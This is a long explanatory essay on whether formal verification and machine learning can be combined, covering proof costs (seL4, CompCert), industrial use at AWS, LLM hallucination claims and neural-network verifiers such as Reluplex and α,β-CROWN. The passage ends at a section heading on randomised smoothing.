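# Formal methods and machine learning: can strong guarantees be combined with flexibility?

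## What do formal methods and machine learning each offer?

Formal methods are mathematical techniques for stating exactly what a computer system must do and proving that it does so. Engineers use them mostly where a fault could kill people or cost a great deal, as in aircraft software or processor design. Machine learning builds software from examples instead of explicit instructions. It can recognise images, transcribe speech and write text, tasks for which nobody has managed to write down a full set of rules. A proof covers every case that its premises allow, but somebody must first state precisely what to prove. Machine learning doesn't require such a statement, but the resulting model comes without a proof. Researchers have therefore proposed hybrid designs that combine a learned component, for flexibility, with a formal component that proves or enforces some property of the result.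 Researchers disagree about whether such designs keep the benefits of both fields.

### Specifications, proofs and checkers

A specification states, in a language with exact meaning, what a system must or must not do. The implementation is the program, circuit or network that has to satisfy it. A proof is a chain of logical steps establishing that the implementation meets the specification on every input the specification covers, and a checker is a program that accepts or rejects those steps. Alan Turing sketched a version of this approach in the late 1940s, and Floyd, Hoare and Naur made it systematic in the late 1960s (Urban and Miné, 2021, *A Review of Formal Methods applied to Machine Learning*). They proved tiny programs correct with pen and paper. Proofs about real software are far too long for that, so later work in the field has largely focused on developing tools.

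Model checking represents a system as a set of states and the steps between them. A stopwatch, for example, can be stopped, running or paused, and each button press moves it from one state to another. A model checker starts from the initial state and follows every possible step until it has visited every reachable state. *Application of AI to formal methods* (2024) calls a reachable state that violates the specification a counterexample, which means the search has found a fault. Chip makers such as Intel have had success with the method because hardware has a finite number of states. But that number can be very large. Thirty on/off switches already have more than a billion combinations, and compact representations that treat many states at once allow larger systems to be checked but don't remove the limit. If a system is too large or infinite, a person has to write a simplified model, and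 the result then applies to the model, which may not be faithful to the system.

An SMT solver is a program that decides automatically whether any values satisfy a logical formula about numbers, arrays and similar objects. To verify source code with one, the programmer gives each function a precondition, which must hold when the function starts, and a postcondition, which must hold when it returns. This is usually written {P} C {Q}, meaning that if P holds before the commands C run, and C finishes, then Q holds afterwards. Verifiers commonly work backwards from Q. For x to equal 42 after the assignment x := a, a must equal 42 before it. Repeating this step through the whole function gives the weakest condition that guarantees Q, and the solver checks that P implies it. The programmer also has to supply an invariant for each loop, a statement that stays true on every pass, because the verifier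 does not know how many repetitions to work back through. When avionics engineers applied Frama-C, a verification platform for the language C, to single functions, the solver handled 95% of the proof obligations automatically, according to Urban and Miné, and people had to help with the rest.

In proof assistants such as Lean, Isabelle and Rocq (formerly Coq), the user works out most of the proof and writes it in a formal language. The software automates some routine steps, and a small core program called the kernel checks the whole proof. The logic can express advanced mathematics, so the limits are the user's ingenuity and patience. The best-known result for software is CompCert, a C compiler (a program that translates C into machine code). Its designers proved in Coq that the machine code behaves as the source code does, as long as the C language defines the meaning of every operation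 in the source.

### One input in four billion

The difference between testing and proof is easiest to see in a small program. The function below returns the absolute value of a 32-bit integer, a standard format for whole numbers in C and Java. Its specification is that the result is never negative.

```
int abs(int x) {
  if (x < 0) return -x;
  return x;
}
```

The absolute-value function meets its specification for all but one of its 4,294,967,296 possible inputs. The exception is −2,147,483,648, which has no positive counterpart because 32-bit integers only go up to 2,147,483,647. Negating it in Java returns the same negative number, and C leaves the outcome undefined. Java's maintainers call the Java result surprising in OpenJDK's *add Math.absExact*, which records their addition of a second version of the function that throws an error on that input. The fault does occur in practice.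 Error Prone's *MathAbsoluteNegative*, a warning in a code-checking tool, concerns programmers who apply the function to random numbers to make them positive and, on rare occasions, get a negative one.

If a tester runs the function on a million random inputs, the chance of hitting the bad one is 1 − (1 − 2⁻³²)^1,000,000, or about 0.02%. She would need about three billion tests for an even chance of finding the fault. An experienced tester would find it in a second by trying the extreme values first, but only because experience has taught her to look there.

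A verifier treats the input x as an unknown, combines a description of the code with the negation of the specification, and uses a solver to check whether any x satisfies both. If x is zero or more, the function returns x, which cannot be negative. If x is below zero, the function returns −x, and in 32-bit arithmetic that wraps round, as Java's does, this result is still negative for exactly one value, −2,147,483,648. That value satisfies the formula and reveals the bug. CppVerify's *Your first verified function*, a chapter from the manual of a small verifier, works through this case. Without a precondition, the tool rejects the function and reports the lowest integer as a counterexample. Once the programmer adds the precondition that x is at least −2,147,483,647, no value satisfies the formula, which proves that the function meets its specification for every allowed input. Every part of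 the program that calls the function must then provably avoid passing it the excluded value.

In his *ACM Turing Lecture 1972*, Edsger Dijkstra called testing a very effective way to show the presence of bugs but "hopelessly inadequate for showing their absence". This is slightly too strong as a general statement. *Testing can show the presence of bugs but not the absence*, a newsletter essay on Dijkstra's remark, points out that a function with finitely many inputs can be tested on all of them, and that such a test is a proof. A fast computer can test the absolute-value function on all four billion 32-bit inputs in seconds. Testing a function of two 32-bit integers in the same way would take more than 580 years at a billion tests a second.

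A verifier is sound if every program it accepts is correct, as the tool models it, and complete if it accepts every correct program. A sound verifier for 32-bit arithmetic must therefore reject the absolute-value function without its precondition. An incomplete verifier might reject the function even with the precondition. Rice's theorem implies that no tool can decide for every program whether it is correct. Designers must therefore give up full automation, generality or completeness, according to Urban and Miné, who treat soundness as a requirement for every formal method.

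Incompleteness often comes from over-approximation, the use of a model that includes every behaviour the real program can show and possibly some it cannot. For example, a tool might record only the range of each variable. If x lies between −10 and 10, the tool multiplies that range by itself and calculates that x times x lies between −100 and 100. It then raises a false alarm that the square could be negative. But it cannot miss a real error, because the calculated range includes every value the square can take.

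A failed test reveals a real failure, but a suite of passed tests can still miss many bugs. A sound verifier catches every violation of the specification but can also raise false alarms. The newsletter essay concludes from this that testing is the more robust method, because a little testing may find a real bug while a little verification achieves almost nothing. That seems too pessimistic for small functions, since CppVerify needed only one line of specification to expose a bug that a million random tests would almost surely miss. The argument is stronger for large programs, where a failed proof may mean that there is a bug or that the solver needs hints, and somebody has to work out which.

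Soundness also depends on the model. In *Introduction to C program proof with Frama-C and its WP plugin*, Blanchard (2020) gives Frama-C the absolute-value function without a precondition, and the tool accepts it. When he turns on the checks for runtime errors, Frama-C flags the negation as a possible overflow, but the solver times out without identifying the input. The guide to Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, presents the same function, and Dafny proves it correct for all integers. Dafny's integers are unbounded, so every negative number has a positive counterpart. The two tools check the same function under different assumptions about arithmetic, and a reader who sees only the word "verified" will not know which assumption was used.

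### Learning from examples

All of this requires a specification, and for many useful tasks nobody has one. *Using Machine Learning Safely in Automotive Software* (2018) raises the question of what the specification for recognising a pedestrian is. Engineers do write requirements for such components. In an example from *Guidance on the Assurance of Machine Learning in Autonomous Systems (AMLAS)* (2021), a detector 50 metres away must identify pedestrians "on or close to the crossing in their correct position". People understand this requirement well enough, but no verifier can use it. A formal version would need a condition on the millions of numbers in a camera image that holds exactly when the image shows a pedestrian, including one in a wheelchair, one in a carnival costume and one half hidden behind a van.

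Machine learning gets round the missing condition by starting from cases. Developers collect images, and people label each one according to whether it contains a pedestrian. The developers then choose a neural network, which is a function with a large number of adjustable values, its parameters. The network turns an image into a probability that a pedestrian is present. A loss function measures how badly each answer compares with the label. A common choice is −log p, where p is the probability the network gave to the correct label: 0.9 costs about 0.1, and 0.01 costs 4.6. Training is the search for parameters θ that make the average loss small,

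L(θ) = (1/n) · Σ ℓ(f_θ(xᵢ), yᵢ),

where the xᵢ are the n images, the yᵢ their labels, f_θ the network and ℓ the loss on one example. The optimiser computes in which direction a small change to each parameter would lower L, changes all of them slightly in that direction, and repeats this a great many times. No step requires a definition of a pedestrian. A large language model (LLM) comes out of the same procedure with text in place of images and the next word, or fragment of a word, as the label.

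The loss function is mathematically exact, but it is not a specification, because it covers only the n training examples, while a specification covers every input of a kind, possibly infinitely many. For this reason, *Using Machine Learning Safely in Automotive Software* rejects the training set as a substitute for a specification. The optimiser tunes the network to succeed on the training images, so success on them is not an independent check. Developers test whether the network also works on new images by keeping some labelled images out of training and scoring the network on those.

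Such a score estimates an average. Suppose the network labels 10,000 fresh images without a mistake. If those images are a random sample of what the car will meet, we can conclude with 95% confidence that the error rate is below roughly 3 in 10,000. A camera that takes 30 frames a second produces 108,000 an hour, so an error rate at that bound would still mean about 32 mislabelled frames an hour. Because neighbouring frames resemble one another, the errors may well occur in consecutive frames of the same person.

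The estimate also does not bound the worst case. The absolute-value function is correct on 99.99999998% of random inputs, but it always fails on the lowest integer. An attacker who knows this can send that integer deliberately, and a program that used it to mark missing data would trigger the fault whenever data was missing. Average accuracy depends on how often each input occurs, so a test score applies only to conditions like those of the test. The worst case is harder to find for images than for integers, because nobody can list every image or say in advance which are the extreme values. According to *Safety Monitoring of Machine Learning Perception Functions* (2024), validation across all the conditions in which a vehicle operates is impossible, and a network's own confidence is a poor warning because the network can be highly confident when it is wrong. Researchers can prove some narrower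 properties of a trained network, but not that it recognises pedestrians.

### Guarantee, usability and trustworthiness

Comparisons between the two fields tend to treat three separate qualities as one. In *Learning-Infused Formal Reasoning*, for instance, Beg, O'Donoghue and Monahan (2026) call learned systems hard to trust because they are opaque, can fail without warning and offer no clear guarantees. A missing guarantee is a reason for caution, but whether a system has a guarantee does not settle whether to rely on it.

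A guarantee consists of a proved conclusion and the assumptions under which the proof holds. In the avionics work that Urban and Miné describe, the Frama-C proofs about single functions assume that no arithmetic overflow occurs. A second tool, Astrée, establishes that assumption by analysing the whole program. Both tools work on the C source, so CompCert is needed to carry their results over to the machine code that runs on the aircraft.

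A method's usability depends on who can apply it, to what, and with how much effort. The effort can differ sharply between a tool's makers and its users. Proving the CompCert compiler correct took its designers a massive effort, but programmers can compile code with it effortlessly. In the B method, engineers refine an abstract specification step by step into a program and prove each step. This gives a strong guarantee for programs built from scratch but is of little use to a company with a million lines of existing code. Zhang, Cai and colleagues (2024), in *The Fusion of Large Language Models and Formal Methods for Trustworthy AI*, name steep learning curves and the lack of friendly interfaces among the main obstacles to wider use of formal methods. By contrast, anyone who can type a question can use an LLM on almost any subject, but the answer may sound fluent and still be false.

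A system is trustworthy if people are justified in relying on it, which depends on what they rely on it for. A function that always returns 0 can be proved never to return a negative number, but it would be a mistake to rely on it to compute absolute values. A pedestrian detector that misses one person in a hundred may be a reasonable way to count visitors to a park, but using it as the only trigger for a car's brakes would be indefensible.

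People can also have good reasons to rely on a system without a proof. *Ergo, SMIRK is Safe* (2022) presents a safety case, a structured argument backed by evidence, for a learned component that recognises pedestrians in an emergency braking system. Its developers required the component to perform satisfactorily in normal operation and to reject input unlike its training data, so that the car does not brake unnecessarily. The evidence that these are the right requirements includes a formal inspection, which is a structured review by people. The safety case is not a proof, and a critic can dispute any step of it. Its strength also depends on the rest of the vehicle. Under the AMLAS guidance, a backup that does not use machine learning can reduce what engineers have to show about the learned component.

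## Why are the two said to need each other?

Formal methods and machine learning are said to need each other because each might make up for the other's weakness. Proofs about real software take years of skilled labour, and learned systems make errors that nobody can rule out beforehand. A hybrid might take less labour than proof alone and be more dependable than learning alone.

### What proofs have cost

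The developers of seL4 recorded in unusual detail how much work a large proof took. seL4 is a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that runs with full control of the hardware. Trustworthy Systems, the research group that built it, counts 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly code. The proof covers 7,500 of the lines of C, but not the assembly code or the code that starts the machine. It is 200,000 lines long in the proof assistant Isabelle, about 27 for each line of C it covers, and the whole project took roughly 25 person-years.

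About 20 person-years of that time went into the proof, and 2.2 went into writing the kernel, including a prototype in another language. Nine of the 20 went into tools, libraries and other groundwork that was not specific to seL4. The team therefore expected a similar kernel to need only 8 person-years in all, twice what a standard cost model predicts for an ordinary kernel of that size. That forecast presumably assumes people who already know the tools.

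Before verification began in earnest, student projects and an adaptation to another processor had found 16 defects in the C code. Verification found another 144, many of them simple mistakes such as typos.

Whenever a verified program changes, its proof must change too. When the seL4 team added a small system call that bundled existing ones, the code took a day and the proof took less than a week. A new way of handling replies between programs changed less than 5% of the code but took about a person-year to verify again, because it broke properties that the rest of the proof relied on. A company that rewrites its product every few weeks could not easily keep its proof up to date.

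CompCert, the verified C compiler, took less work than seL4. In *Verifying a compiler*, Leroy (2011) put the effort at 50,000 lines of Coq and four person-years. In a slightly earlier version, 76% of the lines were proof, 14% defined the compiler's algorithms and 10% defined the languages involved. Some of the difference is probably because Leroy wrote the verified parts in Coq's own language and could reason about them directly, whereas the seL4 team had to reason about C. The work has also lasted, and CompCert (2025) documents a version from September 2025 that generates code for four families of processor.

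Model checking needs much less human labour, but a system can have too many states to search. A model checker that visits a million states a second would take 18 minutes to get through the billion or so states of 30 on/off variables, nearly 13 days for 40 variables, and nearly 36 years for 50. Compact representations can shorten the search, but an engineer can't tell how much from the number of variables alone.

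### How companies use them

Despite these costs, some large companies have used formal methods for years. Engineers at Amazon Web Services (AWS), which rents out computing and storage, have used formal specification and model checking since 2011, according to *How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* (2015). Ten years later, Brooker and Desai reported in *Systems Correctness Practices at AWS* that many engineers had struggled with TLA+, the first specification language AWS used, which looks more like mathematics than programming. AWS then turned to P, an existing language for describing systems as state machines that exchange messages, and has developed it further since 2019. The team behind the storage service S3 used P when redesigning the service so that a read always returns the latest write, and removed several design bugs early in development.

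AWS reserves full proof for places where a fault would be especially serious. One is Cedar, a language for rules about who may access what. The Cedar team proved security properties of a version written in Dafny, a language with a built-in verifier, but the production version is in Rust. The team therefore runs both versions on the same inputs and compares the answers. This is a sensible compromise, but it gives a weaker guarantee than proving the properties of the Rust version directly.

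Proof has also saved AWS money. Engineers raised the throughput of RSA encryption on one of the company's processors by up to 94% and proved that the optimised code was still correct. Without a proof, a cautious engineer might well have left such delicate code alone. Brooker and Desai work for AWS, though, and count random testing and simulation among formal and "semi-formal" methods. They don't give the labour cost of the proofs. They name the steep learning curve and the need for specialist expertise as the main barriers to wider use, and expect LLMs to help developers write formal models and specifications.

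Specialists elsewhere see similar barriers. For *The 2020 Expert Survey on Formal Methods*, Garavel, ter Beek and van de Pol put 30 questions to 130 prominent researchers and practitioners. About 68% considered formal methods ready for extensive industrial use "only to a limited extent", and 27% considered them ready without that qualification. As obstacles to adoption, 72% chose engineers' lack of training, 67% the limitations of academic tools and 64% the steep learning curve. Only 27% chose high cost without an immediate benefit. The respondents have built careers on formal methods and may overrate their value, but they have less reason to exaggerate the obstacles. If they are right, lack of skill holds back adoption more than lack of money, and a tool that supplied some of that skill would help a good deal.

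### Where learned systems fall short

An LLM takes little skill to use, unlike formal methods, but it lacks their guarantees. Training rewards it for likely text, which may be false. Researchers call a plausible but wrong output a hallucination. An LLM can also answer the same question differently each time, so one good answer is limited evidence that the next will be good.

Errors matter more as tasks grow longer. Suppose, for simplicity, that a model has the same small chance of making a fatal error in every minute of work. If it completes half of all tasks of length h, its chance of completing a task of length t is 2^(−t/h). A model that completes half of its eight-hour tasks would then reach 80% only on tasks of about two and a half hours, and 99% only on tasks of about seven minutes. Real errors are not spread so evenly, and a model may notice and correct some of its own. Even so, a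 model can do impressively on a long task and still be unreliable on much shorter ones.

### The claim that agents need both

Zhang, Cai and colleagues (2025) argue from these weaknesses that AI agents, which carry out tasks as well as answering questions, can be trustworthy only if they combine LLMs with formal methods. Their position paper for the International Conference on Machine Learning, *Trustworthy AI Agents Require the Integration of Large Language Models*, reaches this conclusion by rejecting four alternatives.

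Proponents of combining the two reject reasoning in natural language alone because nothing guarantees that each step follows from the last. Expert systems, which apply fixed rules written by people, usually treat anything not stated as false, so a medical system with no record of an allergy would conclude that the patient has none. LLMs alone hallucinate, and it is hard to trace how they arrived at an answer. Giving them documents to consult makes them more accurate but doesn't make their reasoning valid. Formal methods alone require hand-written specifications, become harder to apply as the number of possible states grows, and cannot capture every aspect of an unpredictable environment.

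*Trustworthy AI Agents Require the Integration of Large Language Models* includes a worked example about a car that should never let its owner lock the key inside. The researchers asked an August 2024 version of GPT-4o to turn a description of the car into a formal model for a model checker called PAT. The formal model contained the following rule, with its condition in square brackets and its effect in braces.

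```
[key == i && owner[i] == near] leavekey {key = incar;}
```

One rule in the model lets a person who holds the key and stands near the car leave the key inside, whether or not the door is open. PAT searched the reachable states and returned a trace, a sequence of steps ending with the key locked in the car. A short trace of this kind would have the owner lock the door from outside and then put the key in the car. Given the trace, GPT-4o changed the rule so that a person can leave the key in the car only while the door is open. It also tightened the rule for locking, so that a person can lock the door only from inside or while standing outside with the key. PAT found no violation in the repaired model.

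The two tools complement each other in this example because GPT-4o spared the user from learning PAT's language, and PAT found a fault that GPT-4o had missed. The first repaired rule corrects a mistake in the description of the world, since no real owner can push a key through a locked door. The second is a requirement on the car, whose door must stay unlocked if somebody outside tries to lock it without holding the key. If the manufacturer does not build the lock that way, the owner could still be stranded, even though the proof holds for the model.

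PAT could look for a violation only because a property defined what counts as one. Under the repaired rules, a person sitting inside may lock the door with the key on the seat, and whether this is a violation depends on the property's exact wording. A car whose door never locks would also satisfy the property. In the researchers' prototype, an LLM writes the properties as well as the model, so the same misunderstanding can enter both, and PAT would then find nothing wrong. A single example also cannot show how often this loop of checking and repair succeeds.

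### What the hallucination theorem proves

As a further argument against relying on LLMs alone, Zhang and colleagues say that hallucination is mathematically inevitable, citing a 2024 theorem by Xu and colleagues. The theorem treats an LLM as a program that returns an answer to every input. Each input has one right answer, and a model hallucinates if it gets even one input wrong.

For a single model h, the proof is to let f(s) be any answer other than h(s). For a list of models h₁, h₂, h₃ and so on, number all possible inputs s₁, s₂, s₃ and so on, and choose f(sₙ) to differ from the answers that the first n models give to sₙ. Each model hₙ then disagrees with f on sₙ and every later input, so every model on the list gets this one function wrong, however much data its developers used.

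The proof is valid, but it defines the correct answers so that they contradict the models' answers. If the right answer to x + y were defined as x + y + 1, a pocket calculator would get every sum wrong and would hallucinate in the same sense. The theorem doesn't show how often a model errs on the questions people actually ask it, since it holds whether the model is wrong half the time in practice or once in a billion answers.

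The theorem also holds for hybrids. An LLM joined to a checker is still a program, and if it has to answer every input, the same construction yields a function f that it gets wrong. A checker is useful because it lets the system withhold an answer that fails a specification chosen in advance, but that benefit doesn't depend on the theorem. Zhang and colleagues would need measured error rates to support their practical argument, and those rates vary by task and model.

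### Necessary or useful?

Rejecting the four alternatives does not show that formal methods and machine learning need each other either. Each alternative relies on only one technique, so rejecting all four shows at most that some combination is needed, and it could be a different one. For example, a developer might have an LLM write code and then rely on extensive tests, human review and a simple backup system. The safety case for the pedestrian detector SMIRK uses roughly this kind of evidence.

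Garavel and colleagues asked their experts almost the same question about hardware and software in general: is it possible to design trustworthy systems without formal methods? About 38% answered "definitely" or "probably", and 62% "probably not" or "definitely not". Some of the first group pointed to aircraft that people trust although their makers did not use formal methods. Others answered that testing is enough only for simple systems. Part of the disagreement is about the word "trustworthy". If it requires a demonstration that the system meets unambiguous requirements, formal methods are necessary almost by definition. But in the ordinary sense, a system is trustworthy if there are good reasons to rely on it, and the claim that such systems need formal methods is hard to defend when more than a third of the field's own specialists reject it.

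The claim that formal methods need LLMs is weaker still. The seL4 and CompCert teams completed their proofs long before LLMs could help, so formal methods can work without them. LLMs may let more people use formal methods, especially as they begin to reduce the effort of writing proofs. In their 2024 roadmap, Zhang and colleagues claimed only that the combination has "transformative potential", which fits the evidence better than saying the two need each other. The evidence shows that combining them can be useful, and for some tasks it may turn out to be the least laborious way to get a strong guarantee.

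### Three places to put the proof

The usefulness of combining formal methods with machine learning depends on what the formal part proves. Some hybrid designs prove a property of the network, others limit its actions, and others check its output.

To prove a property of a trained network, engineers treat it as a fixed mathematical function. They might prove, for instance, that no sufficiently small change to the pixels of a particular image alters its label, a result known as certified robustness. The property must be expressible as a formula about inputs and outputs. *Trustworthy AI Agents Require the Integration of Large Language Models* acknowledges that LLMs are especially difficult to verify in this way. Their answers vary, most of what users want from them has no formal specification, and the number of possible inputs is enormous. A vocabulary of 100,000 word fragments allows 10⁵⁰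 different prompts of just ten fragments.

If a network is too hard to analyse, engineers can restrict it with a shield, which checks each proposed action and replaces any that could break a safety rule. For example, a learned controller might choose a warehouse robot's speed, under the rule that the robot must be able to stop before the nearest obstacle. If the robot brakes at *a* m/s², it needs *v*²/(2*a*) metres to stop from speed *v*, so when the obstacle is *d* metres away, the shield must keep the speed below √(2*ad*). With *a* = 2 and *d* = 1, the limit is 2 m/s. The proof holds for any controller, even an untrained one, but it assumes that the robot measures *d* correctly, brakes without delay and is on a dry floor.

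Monitoring is weaker than shielding because it detects violations only after they occur, so people can fix the cause but can't undo the action. AWS's PObserve tool, for example, compares the logs of a running system with its specification in P. Zhang and colleagues consider such monitoring a viable long-term approach for LLMs because it examines only the outputs the model produces. They concede that many existing monitors rely on vague, informal properties.

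In the remaining design, a model produces a program, a proof or a plan, and a checker accepts or rejects it before anyone uses it. CompCert already worked this way in one place, without any machine learning. A compiler has to assign a program's variables to a processor's few fast storage slots, called registers, so that no two variables in use at the same time share one. Finding a good assignment is difficult, and so is proving that a search method always finds a valid one, but checking a given assignment is easy. Leroy therefore left the search method unproved and proved that a small checker for its results was correct. If the check fails, the compiler stops.

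An LLM can replace that search method. Its mistakes then waste time and computing power, but a sound checker rejects them. This is the most attractive of the three designs where it applies, because the model can be inventive without having to be reliable. It applies only where someone can specify exactly what counts as a correct product. A checker can compare a sorting program with a definition of sorted order, but it has no such definition for the label "pedestrian".

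### What a combination inherits

Even a system with a correct proof can cause harm. The specification may omit something important, or the proof may rest on a false assumption about the surroundings. There is also a small chance that a faulty checker accepted a bad proof. Without a proof, errors in the implementation come on top. The chance that at least one of these sources causes harm is never greater than the sum of their separate chances:

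P(harm) ≤ p(implementation) + p(specification) + p(surroundings) + p(checker).

This inequality holds whether or not the sources are independent. The table applies it to a system over a year of use, with invented rates.

| Source of harm | Without proof | With proof |
|---|---|---|
| Implementation error | 5% | 0% |
| Omission in the specification | 2% | 2% |
| False assumption about the surroundings | 1% | 1% |
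| Faulty checker | none used | 0.01% |
| Upper bound on harm | 8% | 3.01% |

Proof lowers the bound from 8% to 3.01% because it removes the first term and adds only a very small one. Two sources may cause harm on the same occasions, so the true risk lies between the largest single term and the sum, which is 5% to 8% without the proof and 2% to 3.01% with it. On these figures the proof is worth having, but making it stronger would achieve almost nothing, because two thirds of the remaining bound comes from the specification. The proof removes the first term only if it covers the whole implementation, and in seL4 about 1,200 lines of C remained outside it.

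Introducing a proof may change the other terms. Writing an exact specification and trying to prove properties of it can expose mistakes in the design. The first stage of the seL4 proof led to about 300 changes in the kernel's most abstract specification and 200 in a more detailed one. About half of these changes concerned bugs in the algorithms or design. For a project like that, the 2% would probably fall.

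If an LLM writes the specification, the 2% may rise instead. In an example from the 2024 roadmap by Zhang and colleagues, a user wants to find a day when three people can meet. David is free on Monday or Tuesday, Emma on Tuesday or Wednesday, and Alex on Tuesday or Thursday. The LLM translates this into formulas for Z3, a widely used SMT solver, but leaves out that each person is busy on the other days. Z3 could then correctly return Thursday, which satisfies every formula it received but suits only Alex. A further correction step adds the missing formulas, after which Tuesday is the only solution. If such steps missed enough omissions to raise the specification term from 2% to 7%, the upper bound for the system with a proof would be 8.01%, slightly higher than for the system without one.

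## Can a neural network itself be proved safe?

Engineers can prove useful safety properties of small neural networks, and narrower properties of some much larger ones. They cannot yet do this for anything the size of an LLM, mainly because the number of cases to check can double with every unit in the network.

### The verification problem

A verification query consists of a trained network f, a region X of inputs and a condition on the output. The verifier must either prove that f(x) meets the condition for every x in X or find a counterexample. For certified robustness, X contains every image that differs from a given photograph by at most ε in each colour value, and the condition is that the correct label keeps the highest score.

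Most networks that researchers verify consist largely of ReLU units. Each unit computes a weighted sum z of its inputs and returns max(0, z), so it is off when z is negative and on when z is positive. If every unit stayed either on or off throughout X, the network would be a linear function there, and a standard method called linear programming could check the condition quickly. Usually some units are on for some inputs in X and off for others, and the verifier has to consider both cases. With k such units there can be 2ᵏ combinations, which is about 10⁹⁰ for 300 units.

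*Reluplex*, by Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017), proved that the problem is NP-complete. A method that answered every query quickly would therefore also solve a large family of hard search problems quickly, and most computer scientists doubt that such a method exists. One of these problems, 3-SAT, is to decide whether some choice of true and false for a set of variables makes every clause in a list true, where a clause might be "a or b or not c". *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, by Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), describes test networks that encode 3-SAT.

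A simple network of this kind takes each variable as an input between 0 (false) and 1 (true). For the clause "a or b or not c", the unit ReLU(c − a − b) returns 1 if the clause is false and 0 if it is true. Subtracting all the clause units from 1 gives an output y₁. When every input is 0 or 1, y₁ reaches 1 only if every clause is true, but inputs such as ½ could also make it reach 1 when no true/false assignment satisfies every clause. A second output y₂ rules these out by adding up ReLU(x) − ReLU(2x − 1) over all inputs x, which gives zero only if each x is exactly 0 or 1. Deciding whether any input gives y₁ ≥ 1 and y₂ ≤ 0 is therefore the same as solving the original 3-SAT problem. The theorem concerns the worst case, however, and trained networks are often easier to verify.

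Reluplex, an SMT solver built by Katz and colleagues, avoids checking many of the cases. It extends the simplex method, a classic algorithm for linear inequalities. As *Conv-Reluplex* (2026) describes, the solver temporarily lets a unit's input and output be inconsistent, repairs the inconsistencies as it goes, and splits a unit into on and off cases only if it needs to. Reluplex could handle networks ten times as large as earlier tools could. Its main test was ACAS Xu, a prototype system of 45 small networks that advise aircraft how to turn to avoid a collision. Queries took from seconds to days, and some never finished.

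### Bounds instead of cases

Newer verifiers begin by calculating bounds on what each unit can return. The simplest method, interval propagation, works forwards from the lowest and highest value of each input. Consider this network:

h₁ = ReLU(x₁ − x₂), h₂ = ReLU(x₁ + x₂), y = h₁ − h₂.

Let x₁ lie between 0.9 and 1.1, and x₂ between −0.1 and 0.1. Both sums then lie between 0.8 and 1.2, and so do h₁ and h₂. These intervals allow y to be as low as 0.8 − 1.2 = −0.4 and as high as 0.4, so they are not enough to prove the safety property y > −0.3.

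The property is nevertheless true. Both sums are always positive, so both units are on, and y = (x₁ − x₂) − (x₁ + x₂) = −2x₂, which lies between −0.2 and 0.2. Interval propagation fails to prove this because it treats h₁ and h₂ as independent. In fact, h₁ can be 0.8 only when x₁ is 0.9, and h₂ can be 1.2 only when x₁ is 1.1, so the two values cannot occur together. The over-approximation tends to grow from layer to layer.

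Linear bound propagation, the method behind the CROWN family of verifiers, expresses bounds as linear formulas in the inputs instead of plain numbers. In this example it obtains −2x₂ exactly and proves the property. If a ReLU unit can be on or off, the verifier bounds its output between two straight lines. For z between −0.2 and 0.2, ReLU(z) is at most 0.5z + 0.1 and at least αz for any α between 0 and 1. A refinement called α-CROWN adjusts the α values to tighten the final bounds.

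Even good lines leave a gap between the computed bound and the true maximum. Suppose x₁ now lies between −0.1 and 0.1, like x₂, and the property to prove is that h₁ + h₂ stays below 0.25. Adding the two upper lines gives x₁ + 0.2, which can be as high as 0.3. The true maximum is 0.2, so the property holds, but this bound is too loose to prove it.

Branch and bound closes the gap by splitting the problem only where the bounds are too loose. If the first unit is off, h₁ is zero and h₂ is at most 0.2, which proves that case without splitting the second unit. If the first unit is on, the bound is still 0.3, so the verifier splits the second unit too. With the second unit off, the sum is x₁ − x₂, and with both on, it is 2x₁. Neither can exceed 0.2, so three short proofs cover every input.

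Given enough time and exact arithmetic, branch and bound answers any query about a ReLU network, but the number of subproblems can double with each split. The leading tool, α,β-CROWN, speeds up bound propagation with graphics processors and includes the conditions from each split when it computes the bounds. Which unit the verifier splits first also affects its speed. Davis et al. (2026) report consistent speedups from looking ahead at the effect of possible splits before choosing one.

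### What current tools can prove

Since 2020, researchers have compared their verifiers in an annual competition, VNN-COMP. The main part of the 2026 edition had 3,373 queries about 467 networks. The verifier α,β-CROWN answered 3,164 of them, or 94%, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. The networks in the competition ranged from about 100 parameters to 138 million.

The 94% covers only the benchmark queries, so it doesn't show what share of the properties people care about can be checked. Almost a third of the queries concern sentence classifiers with only about 4,000 parameters. Whoever proposes a benchmark also chooses its difficulty and time limits, and the α,β-CROWN team proposed several of the benchmarks. The same tool solved only 38 of 60 queries that Konstantin Kaulen chose to span a wide range of difficulty.

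Progress on ACAS Xu is easier to judge, because the networks and properties have stayed the same since 2017. In 2026, three tools answered all 186 queries with a limit of 116 seconds per query. They proved that the property held in 139 and found counterexamples in the other 47. Engineers can now repeat this work without a research group, by using a commercial toolbox and following MathWorks' *Verify VNN-COMP Benchmark for ACAS Xu Neural Networks Using α,β-CROWN*.

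Doug Wehbe and Stanley Bak built Vibecheck, one of the strongest verifiers, in two months with Claude Code, an LLM-based programming tool. Vibecheck answered 3,108 queries and came second, and the organisers recorded no incorrect answers from it. This is good evidence that an LLM can help build a capable verifier, but it doesn't prove that Vibecheck is sound.

### What certification costs in accuracy

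Ordinary training produces networks that are accurate but hard to certify. In certified training, developers calculate bounds on the network's output for the whole region around each training image, then train the network to reduce the largest loss those bounds allow, often alongside other losses. This makes the network more robust and the bounds tighter, but it leaves less freedom to fit the images themselves.

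The table gives results from Ladner and colleagues for networks that Kaulen trained with recent methods. Certified accuracy is the share of test images that a network labels correctly and for which α,β-CROWN proved that no allowed change alters the label. CIFAR-10 contains small photographs in ten classes, and TinyImageNet has 200 classes. Colour values run from 0 to 255.

| Images and network | Allowed change per colour value | Ordinary accuracy | Certified accuracy | Undecided after 1,000 seconds |
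|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10 | 2 | 83.54% | 66.04% | 6.58% |
| CIFAR-10, wider network | 2 | 85.37% | 60.28% | 14.33% |
| CIFAR-10 | 8 | 57.19% | 35.49% | 1.34% |
| TinyImageNet | 1 | 41.21% | 27.81% | 2.36% |

Networks trained only for accuracy label well over 95% of CIFAR-10 images correctly. Certification against a change of 2 therefore lowers ordinary accuracy by more than ten percentage points, and certification against a change of 8 lowers it by nearly 40. People can barely see a change of 2, so this is a large loss of accuracy for a modest guarantee.

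Some of the shortfall may come from the verifier. The wider CIFAR-10 network has a lower certified accuracy than the standard one, but α,β-CROWN left more than twice as many of its images undecided. If all the undecided cases were robust, the wider network would have a certified accuracy of 74.61% and the standard one 72.62%. Across all six networks in the test, 2,994 of 60,000 queries timed out after 1,000 seconds each, which adds up to almost 35 days of computing.

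### Randomised smoothing

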